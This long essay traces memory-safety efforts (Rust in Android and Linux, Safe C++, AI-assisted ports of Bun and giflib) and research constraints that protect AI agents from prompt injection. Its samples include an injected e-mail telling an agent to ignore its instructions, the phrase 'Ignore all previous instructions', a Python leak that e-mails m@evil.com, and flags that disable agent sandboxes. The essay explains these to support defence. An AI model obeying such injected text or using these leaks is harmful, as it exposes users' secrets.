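By 2025 Android contained about five million lines of Rust, and Google's developers were adding slightly more Rust than C++. This let Vander Stoep compare the two languages within one project. Google had found one potential memory-safety vulnerability in the Rust code, or an estimated 0.2 per million lines, compared with a historical figure of about 1,000 per million lines for C and C++.

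The estimate rests on a single bug, but its uncertainty is too small to explain that gap. The upper end of a 95% confidence interval for one observed event is 5.6 events, or about one vulnerability per million lines. The Rust code is also younger, so people have had less time to find its errors. At Google's own decay rate, though, they should find about a third of them in the first year, so the code's age might account for a factor of three.

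The one vulnerability was a buffer overflow in unsafe code in CrabbyAVIF, an image-decoding library. Google fixed it before any public release. Android's allocator places guard pages, regions that no program may touch, around large blocks of memory. The overflow ran into a guard page and crashed the program, which alerted the developers and would also have stopped an attacker from exploiting the bug. The crash report did not make clear that an overflow was the cause, which slowed the investigation. Google has since corrected the reporting.

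About 4% of Android's Rust, or some 200,000 lines, is inside `unsafe` blocks. If those lines were as error-prone as C, Google would have expected about 200 vulnerabilities in them. Vander Stoep suggests that Google found fewer because some of Rust's checks still apply inside `unsafe`, programmers hide unsafe code behind small interfaces, and reviewers give it extra attention.

Vander Stoep was most surprised by results unrelated to security. Rust changes needed about 20% fewer revisions than C++ changes of similar size and spent about 25% less time in review. After merging changes, developers had to roll back medium and large ones in Rust about a quarter as often as in C++.

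Google compared only changes by its own Android developers, many of whom write both languages. This reduces the chance that better programmers explain the result, but nobody assigned the work at random. Some of the fourfold difference may arise because developers tend to use Rust for new components, while a C++ change is more likely to touch old code that other parts depend on, where a mistake is easier to make. Even a smaller difference would matter for adoption, because programmers choosing a language had never given reliability much weight, and managers who cared only about schedules now had a reason to choose Rust.

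### A second language in the Linux kernel

Android runs on the Linux kernel, which developers had written in C for three decades. In 2022 Linus Torvalds, who leads Linux, accepted basic support for Rust, and it appeared in version 6.1 that December. The support was officially experimental and aimed mainly at drivers, the parts of a kernel that control particular devices.

A Rust driver still has to call the kernel's C code, so Rust developers write a wrapper for each group of C functions, with unsafe code inside and a safe interface outside. To write one, they need to know which part of the kernel frees each piece of memory and which lock protects it. C does not require programmers to state this, and often only the maintainer of that code knows.

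Some maintainers didn't want to help because they didn't want to learn Rust and expected that changes to their C functions would break wrappers they couldn't repair. The Rust developers offered to make the repairs themselves, but maintainers who accepted would depend on a small group staying for decades. Wedson Almeida Filho, one of the Rust project's main developers, heard this objection from the audience when he presented wrappers for file systems at a conference in May 2024. He resigned that August, blaming "nontechnical nonsense".

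The argument intensified in January 2025 over a Rust wrapper for DMA, which lets devices read and write memory without going through the processor. The wrapper was in a separate directory, and its developers would maintain it. Christoph Hellwig, who helped maintain the C code underneath, still rejected it. He objected to any kernel written in two languages, whatever the second one was. Hector Martin, who led the effort to run Linux on Apple's computers, campaigned against the decision on social media. Torvalds criticised the campaign, and Martin resigned as a kernel maintainer in February.

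Torvalds then ruled that maintainers could ignore Rust and keep it out of their own code, but could not stop other people's Rust code from using the functions they provided. Hellwig stepped down as DMA maintainer soon afterwards. The ruling left most of the work of supporting Rust to the people who wanted it, which addressed the maintainers' main concern that the work would fall on them.

In December 2025 the Linux kernel's senior developers met in Tokyo and agreed that Rust was no longer an experiment and would stay. The kernel also got its first CVE entry for Rust code that month. Unsafe code in an Android driver moved items between linked lists, and two threads could change a list at once and crash the system.

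Rust is still a very small part of the Linux kernel. According to Botmonster Tech's *Big Rust rewrites of 2026* (2026), version 7.3 has about 120,000 lines of Rust, or 0.39% of the total, and more than half of those lines are copied from outside libraries. Some parts of the kernel now accept new drivers only in Rust, so Rust's share should grow, as it did in Android.

The leading Linux developers still differ on how much Rust will achieve. Torvalds said in 2026 that Rust fixes some easy bugs and leaves the logic errors. Greg Kroah-Hartman, who maintains the stable kernel releases, estimated that Rust would have caught 80% of the kernel's past vulnerabilities. These opinions are compatible, since a bug that is easy to fix can still let an attacker in.

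### Government guidance without a mandate

In November 2022 the US National Security Agency (NSA) advised organisations to move to memory-safe languages where they could. In February 2024 the White House's cyber director published *Back to the Building Blocks*, which asked software makers to do the same. The report described spacecraft software as a difficult case because it has to work close to the hardware, respond with predictable timing and avoid garbage collection. C, C++ and Rust meet all three requirements, but nobody had yet proved Rust in space.

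The most specific request came from the Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) and the FBI, in a list of bad practices completed in January 2025. They asked makers of software for critical infrastructure to publish a roadmap by 1 January 2026 explaining how they would remove memory errors from their most exposed code, such as the parts that handle network traffic or encryption. Products that would lose support before 2030 were exempt. In June 2025 the NSA and CISA published a longer paper that recommended starting with new code and cited Android's results.

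All of this was voluntary. A company that ignored CISA's date faced no penalty, whereas the Ada mandate had required projects to get a waiver to use another language. CISA also asked companies only to publish a plan by that date, not to change any code.

In December 2025 Microsoft engineer Galen Hunt announced a goal of removing every line of C and C++ from the company by 2030. Days later he clarified that this was a research project, and Microsoft denied having any plan to rewrite Windows. Botmonster Tech cites an examination of Windows 11 that found Rust in six components, one of them from another company.

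The government probably deserves little credit for the change, because the companies with the best results started before it issued any guidance. Android, for example, adopted Rust in 2021. The agencies may have had more effect by paying for tools. DARPA, the American military's research agency, funds a programme called TRACTOR to translate C into Rust automatically. Intel takes part, and its *IDEAS for TRACTOR* describes the work. The guidance alarmed the people responsible for C++, which the agencies had named as an unsafe language.

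### Two plans for a safer C++

The C++ standards committee had two proposals to consider. Sean Baxter, who had written a C++ compiler alone, published *Safe C++* in September 2024. The proposal would add Rust's main ideas to C++, including a borrow checker and `unsafe` blocks. Programmers would mark functions as safe, and the compiler would guarantee memory safety inside them. Safe functions would need a new standard library, because the existing one cannot express how long a reference stays valid.

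Bjarne Stroustrup, who created C++, and Herb Sutter, a long-time leader of the committee, favoured Profiles. A profile is a named set of restrictions and run-time checks that a programmer can switch on for existing code. For example, a bounds profile might forbid pointer arithmetic and check every array index. Stroustrup and Sutter wanted owners of old programs to gain some safety with few changes to their source code.

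The dispute turned on whether a compiler could catch uses of freed memory without the extra information that Rust programmers write. Take this function:

```cpp
void add(std::vector<int>& prices, int& first) {
    prices.push_back(50);
    first = 0;
}
```

If `first` refers to a number stored somewhere else, the function is safe. If somebody calls `add(prices, prices[0])`, `push_back` may free the memory that `first` refers to, and the next line writes to it. The function's type is the same in both cases. Baxter argued that a checker that reads one function at a time must therefore either miss the error or reject much correct code. Rust rejects the call because it would need two mutable references to the same list.

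Sutter's side answered that C++ programmers would not adopt a system that required new annotations throughout their code and a second library. In November 2024 the committee's safety group took a poll on where to spend its time. Nineteen people chose Profiles, nine chose Safe C++ and eleven wanted both. Baxter later stopped work on Safe C++, saying the committee did not like Rust's approach to safety. But Profiles were not ready, and in early 2025 the committee left them out of the 2026 standard. C++26 therefore has a hardened library but no general protection against using freed memory.

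Each camp had a good argument for a different kind of code. Owners of old C++ programs have little use for a system that requires rewriting them, while Android's results favour a strict guarantee for new code. But a company willing to learn new rules for new code can use Rust, which already has libraries and trained programmers. This left Safe C++ with a narrower audience, mainly teams whose new code has to work closely with old C++.

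### Bun moves to Rust in eleven days

In 2026 AI agents made it much cheaper to rewrite a large program, which everyone in these disputes had assumed was too expensive. Agents also write a lot of new Rust. Matsakis (2026), in *What agents mean for Rust (and vice versa)*, quotes the Rust developer David Tolnay as saying that engineers at Meta had written twice as much Rust so far that year as in the previous nine years combined. Matsakis thinks Rust suits agents because its compiler rejects many of their mistakes immediately, although he has also seen them misunderstand a program's logic in ways that no type checker would detect.

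The best-documented port is of Bun, a program that runs JavaScript outside a browser. Its creator, Jarred Sumner, had written it in Zig, where programmers free memory themselves, as in C. A garbage collector frees JavaScript objects, and mixing the two kinds of memory kept causing leaks and crashes. In *Rewriting Bun in Rust*, Sumner (2026) estimates that a rewrite by hand would have taken three engineers a year, with no other improvements in the meantime, so the team would never have done it. For the port, he used an unreleased Claude model from Anthropic, which bought Bun in 2025 and employs him.

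The port covered 535,496 lines. Sumner deliberately kept the structure of the Zig code and proceeded in steps:

- Sumner and Claude spent about three hours writing a guide to translating Zig patterns into Rust.
- Agents examined every field of every data structure to work out how long its contents had to stay valid.
- After a trial on three files, agents translated all 1,448. Two other agents reviewed each piece of code. They saw only the change, not the author's reasoning, and had instructions to find faults.
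- More agents fixed the compiler's errors, and then the failures in Bun's tests.

Bun's tests, which make more than a million individual checks, were written in TypeScript, so they worked unchanged on the new version. Up to 64 copies of Claude worked at once, and Sumner merged the result after 11 days, when every test passed. The computing would have cost about $165,000 at Anthropic's public prices.

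The reviewers caught errors that the compiler had accepted. In one case, the new code handed a piece of memory to a C library to free later, but Rust freed it at the end of the block as usual. The library would then have used the freed memory and freed it again.

Other errors got through. Within days of the merge, somebody reported that the code failed basic tests in Miri, the interpreter that detects undefined behaviour. As Random Chaos' *Bun Rust rewrite* explains, the problem was a type for storing file paths. In simplified form, this was enough to read freed memory:

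```rust
let path = PathString::init(&name);
drop(name);
path.slice();
```

None of these lines needs `unsafe`. `PathString` kept a plain address, as the Zig version had, and an `unsafe` block inside it relied on the address still being valid. The compiler could no longer track that `path` depended on `name`. The proposed repair, according to *Bun Rust Rewrite* (2026), was to mark `init` as unsafe, which makes callers responsible for keeping the memory alive. Sumner had left Zig because of this type of bug, and a faithful translation had carried the design behind it into Rust.

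A week after the merge, and before any release, Bun (2026) published an AI-generated audit of the port. It counted 13,365 `unsafe` blocks and estimated that programmers could replace about 9,300 of them with safe code. The first task it listed was to repair functions that were declared safe but were not. In July about 13,000 uses of the keyword remained, covering about 4% of the code. Android has the same percentage, but its developers had designed their unsafe code for Rust, so the proportion alone is a poor measure of the risk. The Rust Project warns that Miri checks only the particular runs it observes and cannot show that a library is safe for every caller, so passing Miri would not prove the port safe either.

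The port still improved Bun. Sumner lists 128 bugs in the last Zig version that the Rust version fixes, and 19 new bugs that the port introduced, all since fixed. One of the 19 was a wrong constant that made an indexing error inherited from the Zig version easier to reach. Rust's bounds checks stopped the program, whereas the Zig version, which ran without such checks on Mac and Linux, would have written past the end of a list. Willison (2026) notes that Anthropic's coding tool, Claude Code, had been running on the Rust version since 17 June and that few users noticed.

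### What a cheap port depends on

In a larger port that took longer, GitHub's engineers and their agents moved the software behind its Copilot coding agent to more than 800,000 lines of Rust in about 14.5 weeks. InfoQ's *Github Migrates Copilot Runtime to Rust with AI-Assisted Rewrite* (2026) reports that they made 128 separate changes, with old and new parts working together, and kept releasing new versions throughout. Toub (2026), in *Migrating the GitHub Copilot runtime to Rust, using Copilot*, says such a rewrite was not affordable before agents. Jovanović (2026), in *GitHub Copilot Runtime Rust Migration*, questions the headlines that credited the port to one engineer and $120,000 of computing. The old version was in TypeScript, which is already memory-safe, so the port is evidence about the cost of changing languages, not the benefits of memory safety.

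Two Rust versions of curl, a widely used download tool, appeared in the second half of 2026, and one reportedly cost $8,600. Daniel Stenberg, who maintains curl, responds in *Actual curl rewrites in rust* (2026) that writing the code once was never the hard part. He says AI agents could do it because curl has thorough documentation and thousands of tests, and because AI models had trained on its source code for years. He adds that curl came from decades of decisions and user feedback, and that somebody would have to continue that work on the new version. *Rewriting in Rust* (Maćkowski and Grzelak, 2026) lists an earlier attempt to use a Rust library inside curl among the projects that failed, and recommends expanding the use of Rust gradually.

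Bun's million checks gave it the same advantage. Many old C programs have few tests and no living expert. An agent's translation of such a program may compile and still behave differently from the original without anyone noticing.

Google's security team dealt with this problem by testing the new program against the old one. Google's *Scaling Memory Safety* describes using AI to rewrite giflib, a C library that reads and writes GIF images, in Rust. The library has only about 3,000 lines, but it is a good target for attackers because it processes images from untrusted sources. According to a Taiwanese news report by 何 (2026), *谷歌Gemini AI助C程式碼移植Rust 意外揪出零日漏洞*, Google's Gemini model translated the code and kept the original function names so that existing C programs could use the new library. Engineers had to correct the model's handling of ownership and lifetimes, especially where the Rust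 code interacted with C. InfoQ's *Google Rewrites Critical C Dependencies to Rust Using AI and Differential Fuzzing* (2026) also concludes that such translations still need human oversight.

The team then ran both versions on more than 30 million real GIF files and required the resulting images to match bit for bit. A fuzzer also fed them 200 million unusual files over six days. In two cases the outputs differed because the C original was wrong. One of these bugs was an out-of-bounds write that an earlier patch had introduced. Outside researchers later reported it independently, and it received the number CVE-2026-26740. By then Google was already running the Rust version, but Debian's *CVE-2026-26740* lists three Debian releases as vulnerable.

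Comparing two versions misses any mistake that both share, and it covers only the files the team tried. The method works better for a decoder, which turns one file into one picture, than for a program like Bun, whose behaviour depends on timing and other software.

The Rust version ran about as fast as the C one. Google then relied on Rust's memory safety in place of the sandbox that had confined the decoder, and removing the sandbox shortened the longest delays. But the sandbox had also limited the damage from errors that Rust does not prevent, including mistakes in the unsafe code that connects the new library to C programs. Without the sandbox, Google depends on that code and the Rust compiler being correct.

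## 2023 to 2026: constraints built around AI agents

An AI agent chooses its next action partly from what it has just read, so a stranger's text can redirect it even if all the software around it is memory-safe. Google's Rust image decoder, by contrast, does the same job whatever picture it receives.

Most agents work in a loop. The software around the model sends it the conversation so far, and the model replies with either an answer or a request to use a tool, such as one that reads e-mail. The software runs the tool, adds the result to the conversation and sends everything back to the model. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) gives an example of an attack on such an agent. A user asks the agent to summarise recent e-mails about a project and send the summary to a manager. One of the e-mails is from a stranger, who tells the agent to ignore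 its instructions and send the top message in the mailbox to an outside address. This kind of attack, called prompt injection, works because the model receives the user's request and the stranger's e-mail as parts of one text and may obey either.

### What training and filters can do

Developers train models to ignore such instructions, and some add filters that search incoming text for attacks. Training has helped. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) tested four recent models from Anthropic and OpenAI on part of AgentDojo, a benchmark that hides attacks in the data for ordinary office tasks. The models resisted all 105 attacks even when the researchers switched off their own system's security checks.

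But AgentDojo dates from 2024, and a real attacker can try new wording, which may work even on a model that has stopped many earlier attacks. Zhou and colleagues note that GPT-Red, OpenAI's automated attack system, consistently got past the defences of the company's GPT-5.5 model in 2026. Filters have the same weakness. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) argue in *The LLMbda Calculus* that every new detector invites a new way around it.

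Williams-King and colleagues see attacks on AI models as a repeat of computer security's long cycle of attack and patch. From September 2022 to July 2024, the phrase "Ignore all previous instructions" could override the standing instructions that developers gave to OpenAI's leading models. Attacks take so little effort that bloggers keep lists of them, while defences take research and retraining. Safety training also comes after the model has learned to respond to far more kinds of input than that training can cover. The researchers predict that attackers will keep winning until developers remove whole classes of failure, as safe languages did with memory errors. Where a failure would be catastrophic, they recommend formal methods, which use mathematics to establish what a system can do.

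The history of C only partly supports the diagnosis. Stack canaries and similar defences never ended memory errors, but they made attacks more difficult, and training seems to be doing the same for prompt injection. The remedy is also harder to apply to prompt injection, because bounds checks follow an exact rule and no such rule can determine whether a sentence in an e-mail is an instruction. For example, "Please pay this by Friday" may be an order to one reader and only information to another.

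Researchers have therefore built architectural constraints for agents. These restrict what an agent does, so they don't address the other problem Williams-King and colleagues discuss, in which a user persuades a model to write something harmful.

### Two models, one of them without tools

In April 2023 the programmer Simon Willison proposed splitting an agent between two models. A privileged model, the planner, can use tools but never reads untrusted text. A quarantined model reads the untrusted text but has no tools. The planner refers to the text only by the name of a variable. Costa and colleagues show how such an agent could summarise three e-mails and send the result as a message:

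```
read_emails(number=3)
query_llm(prompt="Summarize ...", input=#read_emails_0)
send_message(to=user, message=#query_llm_0)
```

The software stores the e-mails under the name `#read_emails_0` and gives the planner only that name. The quarantined model writes the summary, which the software stores under another name and inserts into the message.

Keeping untrusted text away from the planner guarantees that the text cannot change which tools the planner uses. The trusted base is the software that enforces this separation and the planner, which still has to understand the user correctly. A malicious e-mail can still make the quarantined model write a false or empty summary.

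An attacker can also change a value that the agent uses in a tool call. Suppose the user asks the agent to send a report to the address that Bob gives in an e-mail. The planner has to get the address from the quarantined model, so an attacker who has altered the e-mail can supply a different one. The agent then makes the tool calls that the user wanted, but sends the report to the attacker. Control-flow integrity left the same gap in C programs, where an attacker could overwrite `is_admin` without redirecting the program.

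### CaMeL: a record for every value

CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2025, closes this gap by tracking where each value came from. *CaMeLoT* (2026), a proposal to extend it, explains the method. The planner first turns the user's request into a program in a restricted form of Python. For the report to Bob, the program might look like this:

```python
email = latest_email(sender="Bob")
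address = ask_quarantined("Which address does Bob give?", email)
report = read_file("report.pdf")
send_email(to=address, attachment=report)
```

A special interpreter runs the program and attaches a record to every value, listing its sources and the people who may read it. The record for `address` shows that it came from an e-mail. The record for `report` might show that only the user and Bob may read it. Before sending anything, the interpreter checks a policy, for example that the recipient is one of the attachment's permitted readers. If the address belongs to a stranger, the interpreter refuses. (CaMeL's developers call these records capabilities, but they are labels on data and do not grant access to anything.)

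CaMeL thus aims to guarantee that a tool runs only if the records for its inputs satisfy the policy, but its developers have not proved that it does. The trusted base includes the interpreter, the policies and the tools that first label the data. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) adds that some features of Python, such as exceptions and the lack of static types, make it hard to give strong guarantees about information flow.

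Estimates of how much CaMeL reduces task completion vary. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) says that CaMeL stopped nearly all of AgentDojo's attacks with little loss in the number of tasks completed. Later tests found a much larger reduction. When Garby and colleagues ran AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks three times each with OpenAI's GPT-5.2, CaMeL completed 67% with its policy checks off and 38% with them on. Zhou and colleagues tested four models on 21 tasks in the office chat program Slack. The models each completed 13 to 17 tasks with the checks off and 4 to 6 with them on.

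*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) predicts that the constraints will prevent fewer tasks from being completed as models get better at planning and writing code. Better models should help with tasks that fail because of a poor plan, but no plan can complete a task that the policy forbids. For instance, the policy forbids some banking tasks that ask the agent to read a file and make the payment it describes.

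### FIDES: labels that restrict the next step

Costa and colleagues' own system, Microsoft's FIDES, also labels data, but its planner chooses one step at a time instead of writing the whole program in advance. Each piece of data has an integrity label, trusted or untrusted, and a confidentiality label that lists its permitted readers. When the agent combines two pieces, the result is trusted only if both were, and only people who could read both may read it:

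{A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}.

FIDES can enforce two policies. One allows an important action, such as a payment, only if nothing untrusted influenced the agent's decision to take it. The other allows the agent to send information only to recipients permitted to read it. With the second policy alone, a malicious e-mail could still make the agent take unwanted actions, but it could not make the agent leak secrets.

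In an ordinary agent, reading a single untrusted e-mail would make the rest of the conversation untrusted and block most later actions. FIDES avoids this by hiding the untrusted parts in variables, as in Willison's design. Sometimes the planner's next step depends on what a variable contains. Suppose the user wants the agent to create a calendar event if any of three e-mails contains a meeting request. The software can restrict the quarantined model to answering "yes" or "no", which the planner reads. A malicious e-mail can change that answer but cannot give the planner other instructions. If the answer is yes, the quarantined model extracts the details, which go into the calendar without passing through the planner.

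Costa and colleagues prove a property called explicit secrecy. If the tool calls that an agent made were run on two sets of stored data that differed only in their secrets, the results would also differ only in their secrets, so those calls did not copy a secret to a public place. But the agent's choice of calls can still reveal something about a secret. If an agent writes to a specialist only when a patient's test is positive, anyone who notices the message learns the result. Costa and colleagues consider a stronger guarantee impractical because it would forbid almost any public action after the agent had read a secret.

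The proof assumes the model always gives the same response to the same input. The trusted base includes the policies, the labels, the tool descriptions and the software that runs the loop.

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, an OpenAI model from 2024. The table leaves out attacks that the benchmark wrongly counted as successful. The last four columns show the share of tasks completed without an attack.

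| Agent | Successful attacks | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, no checks | 152 | 75% | 70% | 99% | 93% |
| Ordinary, with checks | 0 | 37% | 73% | 38% | 20% |
| FIDES, no checks | 21 | 64% | 50% | 65% | 64% |
| FIDES, with checks | 0 | 59% | 41% | 53% | 48% |

The checks stopped every attack on both agents. Hiding data in variables let the agent complete more tasks under the checks in every area except travel, although it still completed far fewer than an unprotected agent. A better model narrowed this gap, and with OpenAI's o1, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks.

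### TACIT: secrets in the type system

CaMeL and FIDES follow data while the agent works. The Scala system of Odersky and colleagues, named TACIT, checks the agent's code before it runs. Its types show which capabilities a function can use. If `f` is a capability for a file, a function that writes text to that file has the type

```scala
String ->{f} Unit
```

`Unit` means the function returns no useful value. A function of type `String -> Unit`, with no braces, uses no capabilities, so it cannot write to a file, print or use the network.

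TACIT uses this distinction to protect secrets. When an agent reads a file from a protected folder, it receives the contents in a wrapper of type `Classified`. The agent can compute with the contents by giving the wrapper's `map` operation a function, but the function must have no side effects, and its result stays wrapped. The compiler rejects this program, slightly shortened from one that an agent wrote in the tests:

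```scala
val key = readClassified("/secrets/api-keys/github.txt")
key.map { k => println(s"GitHub API Key: $k") }
```

Printing needs an output capability, so the function in the second line has the wrong type for `map`. The compiler does accept this program:

```scala
val summary = requestFileSystem("/data") {
  val doc = readClassified("secret/contract.txt")
  chat("Summarize:", doc)
}
println(summary)
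```

The first line gives the agent access to one folder until the closing brace, and the compiler rejects any attempt to keep that access longer. The `chat` function sends the contract to a separate model that the user trusts and returns the answer in a wrapper. The last line shows the summary on the user's screen, but the agent receives only the text `Classified(****)`.

The intended guarantee is that no program the compiler accepts can pass classified data to an unauthorised destination or use a capability that the agent was not given. This guarantee is meant to hold even if the agent's model is working for the attacker, whereas Costa and colleagues assume that the model is honest. The trusted base includes the compiler, the capability library, the software that runs the compiled code and the model that reads the secrets. Researchers have produced computer-checked proofs for the core of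 the type system, but nobody has yet proved that the whole restricted language provides this guarantee.

TACIT does not prevent an agent from giving wrong answers, stop a program from revealing a secret through its running time, or control what other programs do once the agent has started them.

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a software project with a folder of passwords and confidential documents. They combined each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 hidden attacks, giving 120 trials. In 11 more trials, the user asked for secrets directly or pretended to have the authority to see them. They ran all 131 trials on two models, once with the secrets wrapped and once with them as plain text. The table shows how many trials ended without a leak.

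| Model and protection | Hidden attacks | Malicious users | All trials |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, wrapped | 120 of 120 | 11 of 11 | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, plain text | 120 of 120 | 9 of 11 | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, wrapped | 120 of 120 | 11 of 11 | 100% |
| MiniMax M2.5, plain text | 117 of 120 | 3 of 11 | 91.6% |

The models resisted nearly all the hidden attacks on their own, so most of the difference comes from the 11 malicious requests. The perfect scores also don't prove that the guarantee holds, because it depends on the compiler. The most advanced attacks gave the agent ready-made Scala code for reading the secret files. Code that exploits a soundness hole in the compiler, like the ones Claude found in Rust, would be a harder test.

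The protection did not make the agents less useful in these trials. Sonnet completed 99% of the ordinary tasks with the secrets wrapped. Without wrapping it completed 83%, partly because it sometimes stopped to warn the user when it noticed an attack. MiniMax completed 90% with wrapping and 88% without.

On two standard benchmarks, the agents also lost little performance by writing Scala. In simulated customer service for an airline and a shop, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with Scala than with ordinary tool calls. On 300 real software problems, MiniMax solved 41.7% with Scala and 43.3% without. These results measure the effect of using Scala more than the effect of protecting secrets, since the airline tools, for example, return reservations as ordinary data.

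AgentDojo is a better test of how much TACIT's constraints reduce an agent's ability to do ordinary tasks. With OpenAI's o4-mini, TACIT did worse than CaMeL's published results in all four areas, completing 53% of the office tasks against CaMeL's 81%, although Odersky and colleagues describe the two systems' success as comparable. With Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro the results were closer, except in travel, where TACIT completed 64% of the tasks and CaMeL 1%. AgentDojo's scoring counted only one successful attack on TACIT in 1,926 trials, and in that trial the agent had just quoted hotel reviews that the attacker had altered.

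### Language-based agent control

Zhou and colleagues make a more general claim, that any guarantee a language already provides can be extended to agents. In their Haskell system, ELBA, calling an agent is like calling any other function. The developer states the type of the result, the model writes a program of that type, and ELBA runs the program only if it passes the type checker.

Suppose a developer wants an agent to compile bibliographies using only entries from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The developer gives DBLP entries a special type, `Trusted Bib`, that only the library can create. The function that adds an entry to the bibliography accepts only this type, and the type of the agent's program prevents it from using Haskell's ordinary file-writing functions. The agent can still sort and filter entries freely. In a test with about 1,000 citations for each system, an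 ordinary agent with a web search tool got the authors, year or identifier wrong in 19, while ELBA made no such mistakes.

The central theorem concerns the sequences of tool calls that a program e can make, written traces(e). Suppose the language guarantees a property P for every program of type t:

⊢ e : t implies P(traces(e)).

The language's guarantee then also holds for programs that call agents. To prove this, Zhou and colleagues replace each agent call with an ordinary function that requests a program from the model, checks the program's type and runs it. The result is a program in the original language, so the guarantee applies. A generated program may call further agents, up to a fixed depth, and the proof also covers those calls.

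The theorem assumes nothing about how good or honest the model is. But it only gives agents the guarantees that the language and its libraries already have, so any soundness hole in them also affects the agents. The trusted base therefore includes the Haskell compiler and the developer's library. ELBA also relies on Safe Haskell to keep `unsafePerformIO` out of the generated code.

ELBA controls the flow of information with LIO, an existing Haskell library that checks labels at run time. With these checks on, ELBA completed 8 to 10 of the 21 Slack tasks, about twice as many as CaMeL, but took about three times as long.

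AgentDojo's attacks could not show whether the checks worked, because the models ignored all of them. Zhou and colleagues therefore simulated a model that always obeys the attacker, by replacing its task with the attacker's instructions whenever it read them. Up to 42% of the 735 attacks on each model succeeded without the checks, and none succeeded with them. This is stronger evidence for the constraint than the earlier results, because it does not depend on the model resisting attacks.

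### The LLMbda calculus

Garby and colleagues wanted a guarantee that also covers indirect leaks, which explicit secrecy leaves out and CaMeL does not fully prevent. CaMeL would block a program that tests a customer's secret bank balance and sends an e-mail if it is high. It does not block a version like this one:

```python
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
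if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line sets `tmp` to False and CaMeL marks `tmp` as secret. The program then skips the assignment in the fourth line, so `rich` remains True and public, and the program sends the e-mail. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes False and the program sends no e-mail. The recipient learns whether the balance is high because CaMeL changes a variable's label only when an assignment runs. Computer scientists have known about this type of leak since the 1970s. CaMeL makes it difficult for an attacker to get the planner to write such a program, but its label checks are evidently not sound for every program.

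The LLMbda calculus is a small programming language for agents. It labels every value and the conversation with the model, and it stops a program that tries to change a public conversation based on secret information. Garby and colleagues proved a form of noninterference for every program in the language, including those the model writes while the agent is running.

Roughly, noninterference means that changing a secret does not change anything a member of the public can observe. Models respond at random, so the theorem compares probabilities. It also makes an exception for runs that never finish, including those that a policy check stops. Suppose a program fails to finish with probability p given one secret and q given another. Add up the differences in probability over all the results that the public can observe, and call half of that sum Δ. Then

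Δ ≤ (p + q) / 2.

If the program always finishes, Δ is zero and the public learns nothing about the secret.

Garby and colleagues used Lean, a language for computer-checked mathematics, to write both the proof and the interpreter that runs the agents, so the theorem applies to the actual interpreter and not just to a simplified model of it. The trusted base still includes Lean, the code that contacts the AI model over the network, and the tools, whose developers have to label data correctly and check it before sensitive actions. The proof also treats all the agent's tools and data sources as part of the program, which Garby and colleagues acknowledge as a limitation.

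Strict labels would rule out many useful tasks, so the language includes `endorse`, which marks untrusted data as trusted. A second theorem shows that using `endorse` cannot expose secrets, although it can let an attacker influence what the agent does. In Garby and colleagues' test agent, the model decides what to endorse before it reads any untrusted data.

With GPT-5.2, this agent completed 75% of AgentDojo's banking tasks, twice the share that CaMeL completed with its checks on. Attacks succeeded in only 2 of 1,296 runs across three models. About two-thirds of the combinations of task and attack were easy to resist because the attack needed a tool that the agent's plan never used. In both successful attacks, the user had asked the agent to pay a bill described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. The plan had endorsed whatever the file contained. Without `endorse`,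 the agent could not have paid either the false bill or the real one.

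## 2024 to 2026: which patterns have recurred with AI agents

CaMeL and TACIT are research systems, and most people who use an agent encounter simpler limits. The best evidence on how those limits work in practice comes from coding agents, because two major vendors have published figures. Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex read a project's files, edit them and run commands on the programmer's computer. Both products limit what the agent can do there but let the programmer remove the limits.

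### Skipping the prompts

Until August 2026, Claude Code normally asked the user before it ran a command or changed a file. The `--dangerously-skip-permissions` option turned off every prompt. Codex starts with a sandbox, in which the operating system lets its commands write only to the project folder and temporary folders, and blocks the network. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, Codex asks before going outside those limits, unless the user starts it with `--dangerously-bypass-approvals-and-sandbox`, or `--yolo` for short.

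Frequent interruptions push people towards such options. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) describes the problem at OpenAI. Many approval prompts concern mundane actions such as fetching a web page, and an agent left to work on a long job stops at the first prompt. Some users respond by turning off the sandbox. Some Ada projects had likewise used C without requesting a waiver, because asking was unpleasant and nobody checked.

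Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) shows how common this became. A quarter of interactive sessions began with the prompts off. By June 2026, nearly half of the people using the command-line version had written a rule that let some shell commands run without asking. Such rules can be narrow or very broad:

```
Bash(git status)     list the files that have changed
Bash(python:*)       run anything that begins with "python"
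```

A one-line Python program can delete a folder or send it to a stranger, so the second rule permits almost anything. Trębacz and colleagues found that a sizable minority of OpenAI's own users had written such a rule. Another user's settings always allowed the command `codex exec --yolo`, which let an agent inside the sandbox start a second agent outside it.

These hatches differ from Rust's `unsafe` in how much they open and what they leave for a reviewer to find:

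| Hatch | What it permits | What still applies | What a reviewer can find |
|---|---|---|---|
| Rust `unsafe` block | A few extra operations in the marked lines | Type checks, borrow checks and ordinary bounds checks | The marked code |
| Rule for one command | That command | Prompts for other commands | A line in the settings |
| Rule for `python` | Almost anything | Prompts that Python can get around | A line in the settings |
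| Skipping all checks | Every action in the session | The model's training and the limits of the user's account | The option, but not which actions needed it |

A reviewer can read the code in an `unsafe` block before anyone runs it, but an approval rule for an agent covers commands that the model has not yet written. Codex normally searches a stored copy of the web, which reduces its exposure to malicious pages. The `--yolo` option also switches it to live pages, which the option's long name does not suggest, so the user loses the sandbox at the same time as the agent starts reading riskier text.

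Most of the few people who enabled Java's Security Manager likewise granted every permission. Agent vendors now recommend narrower exceptions, and OpenAI advises writing a rule for a specific command instead of broadening the agent's access. OpenAI's *Running Codex safely* describes settings that let an organisation forbid full access for all its staff. Java's developers did something similar with "integrity by default", under which a library cannot exempt itself from the restrictions.

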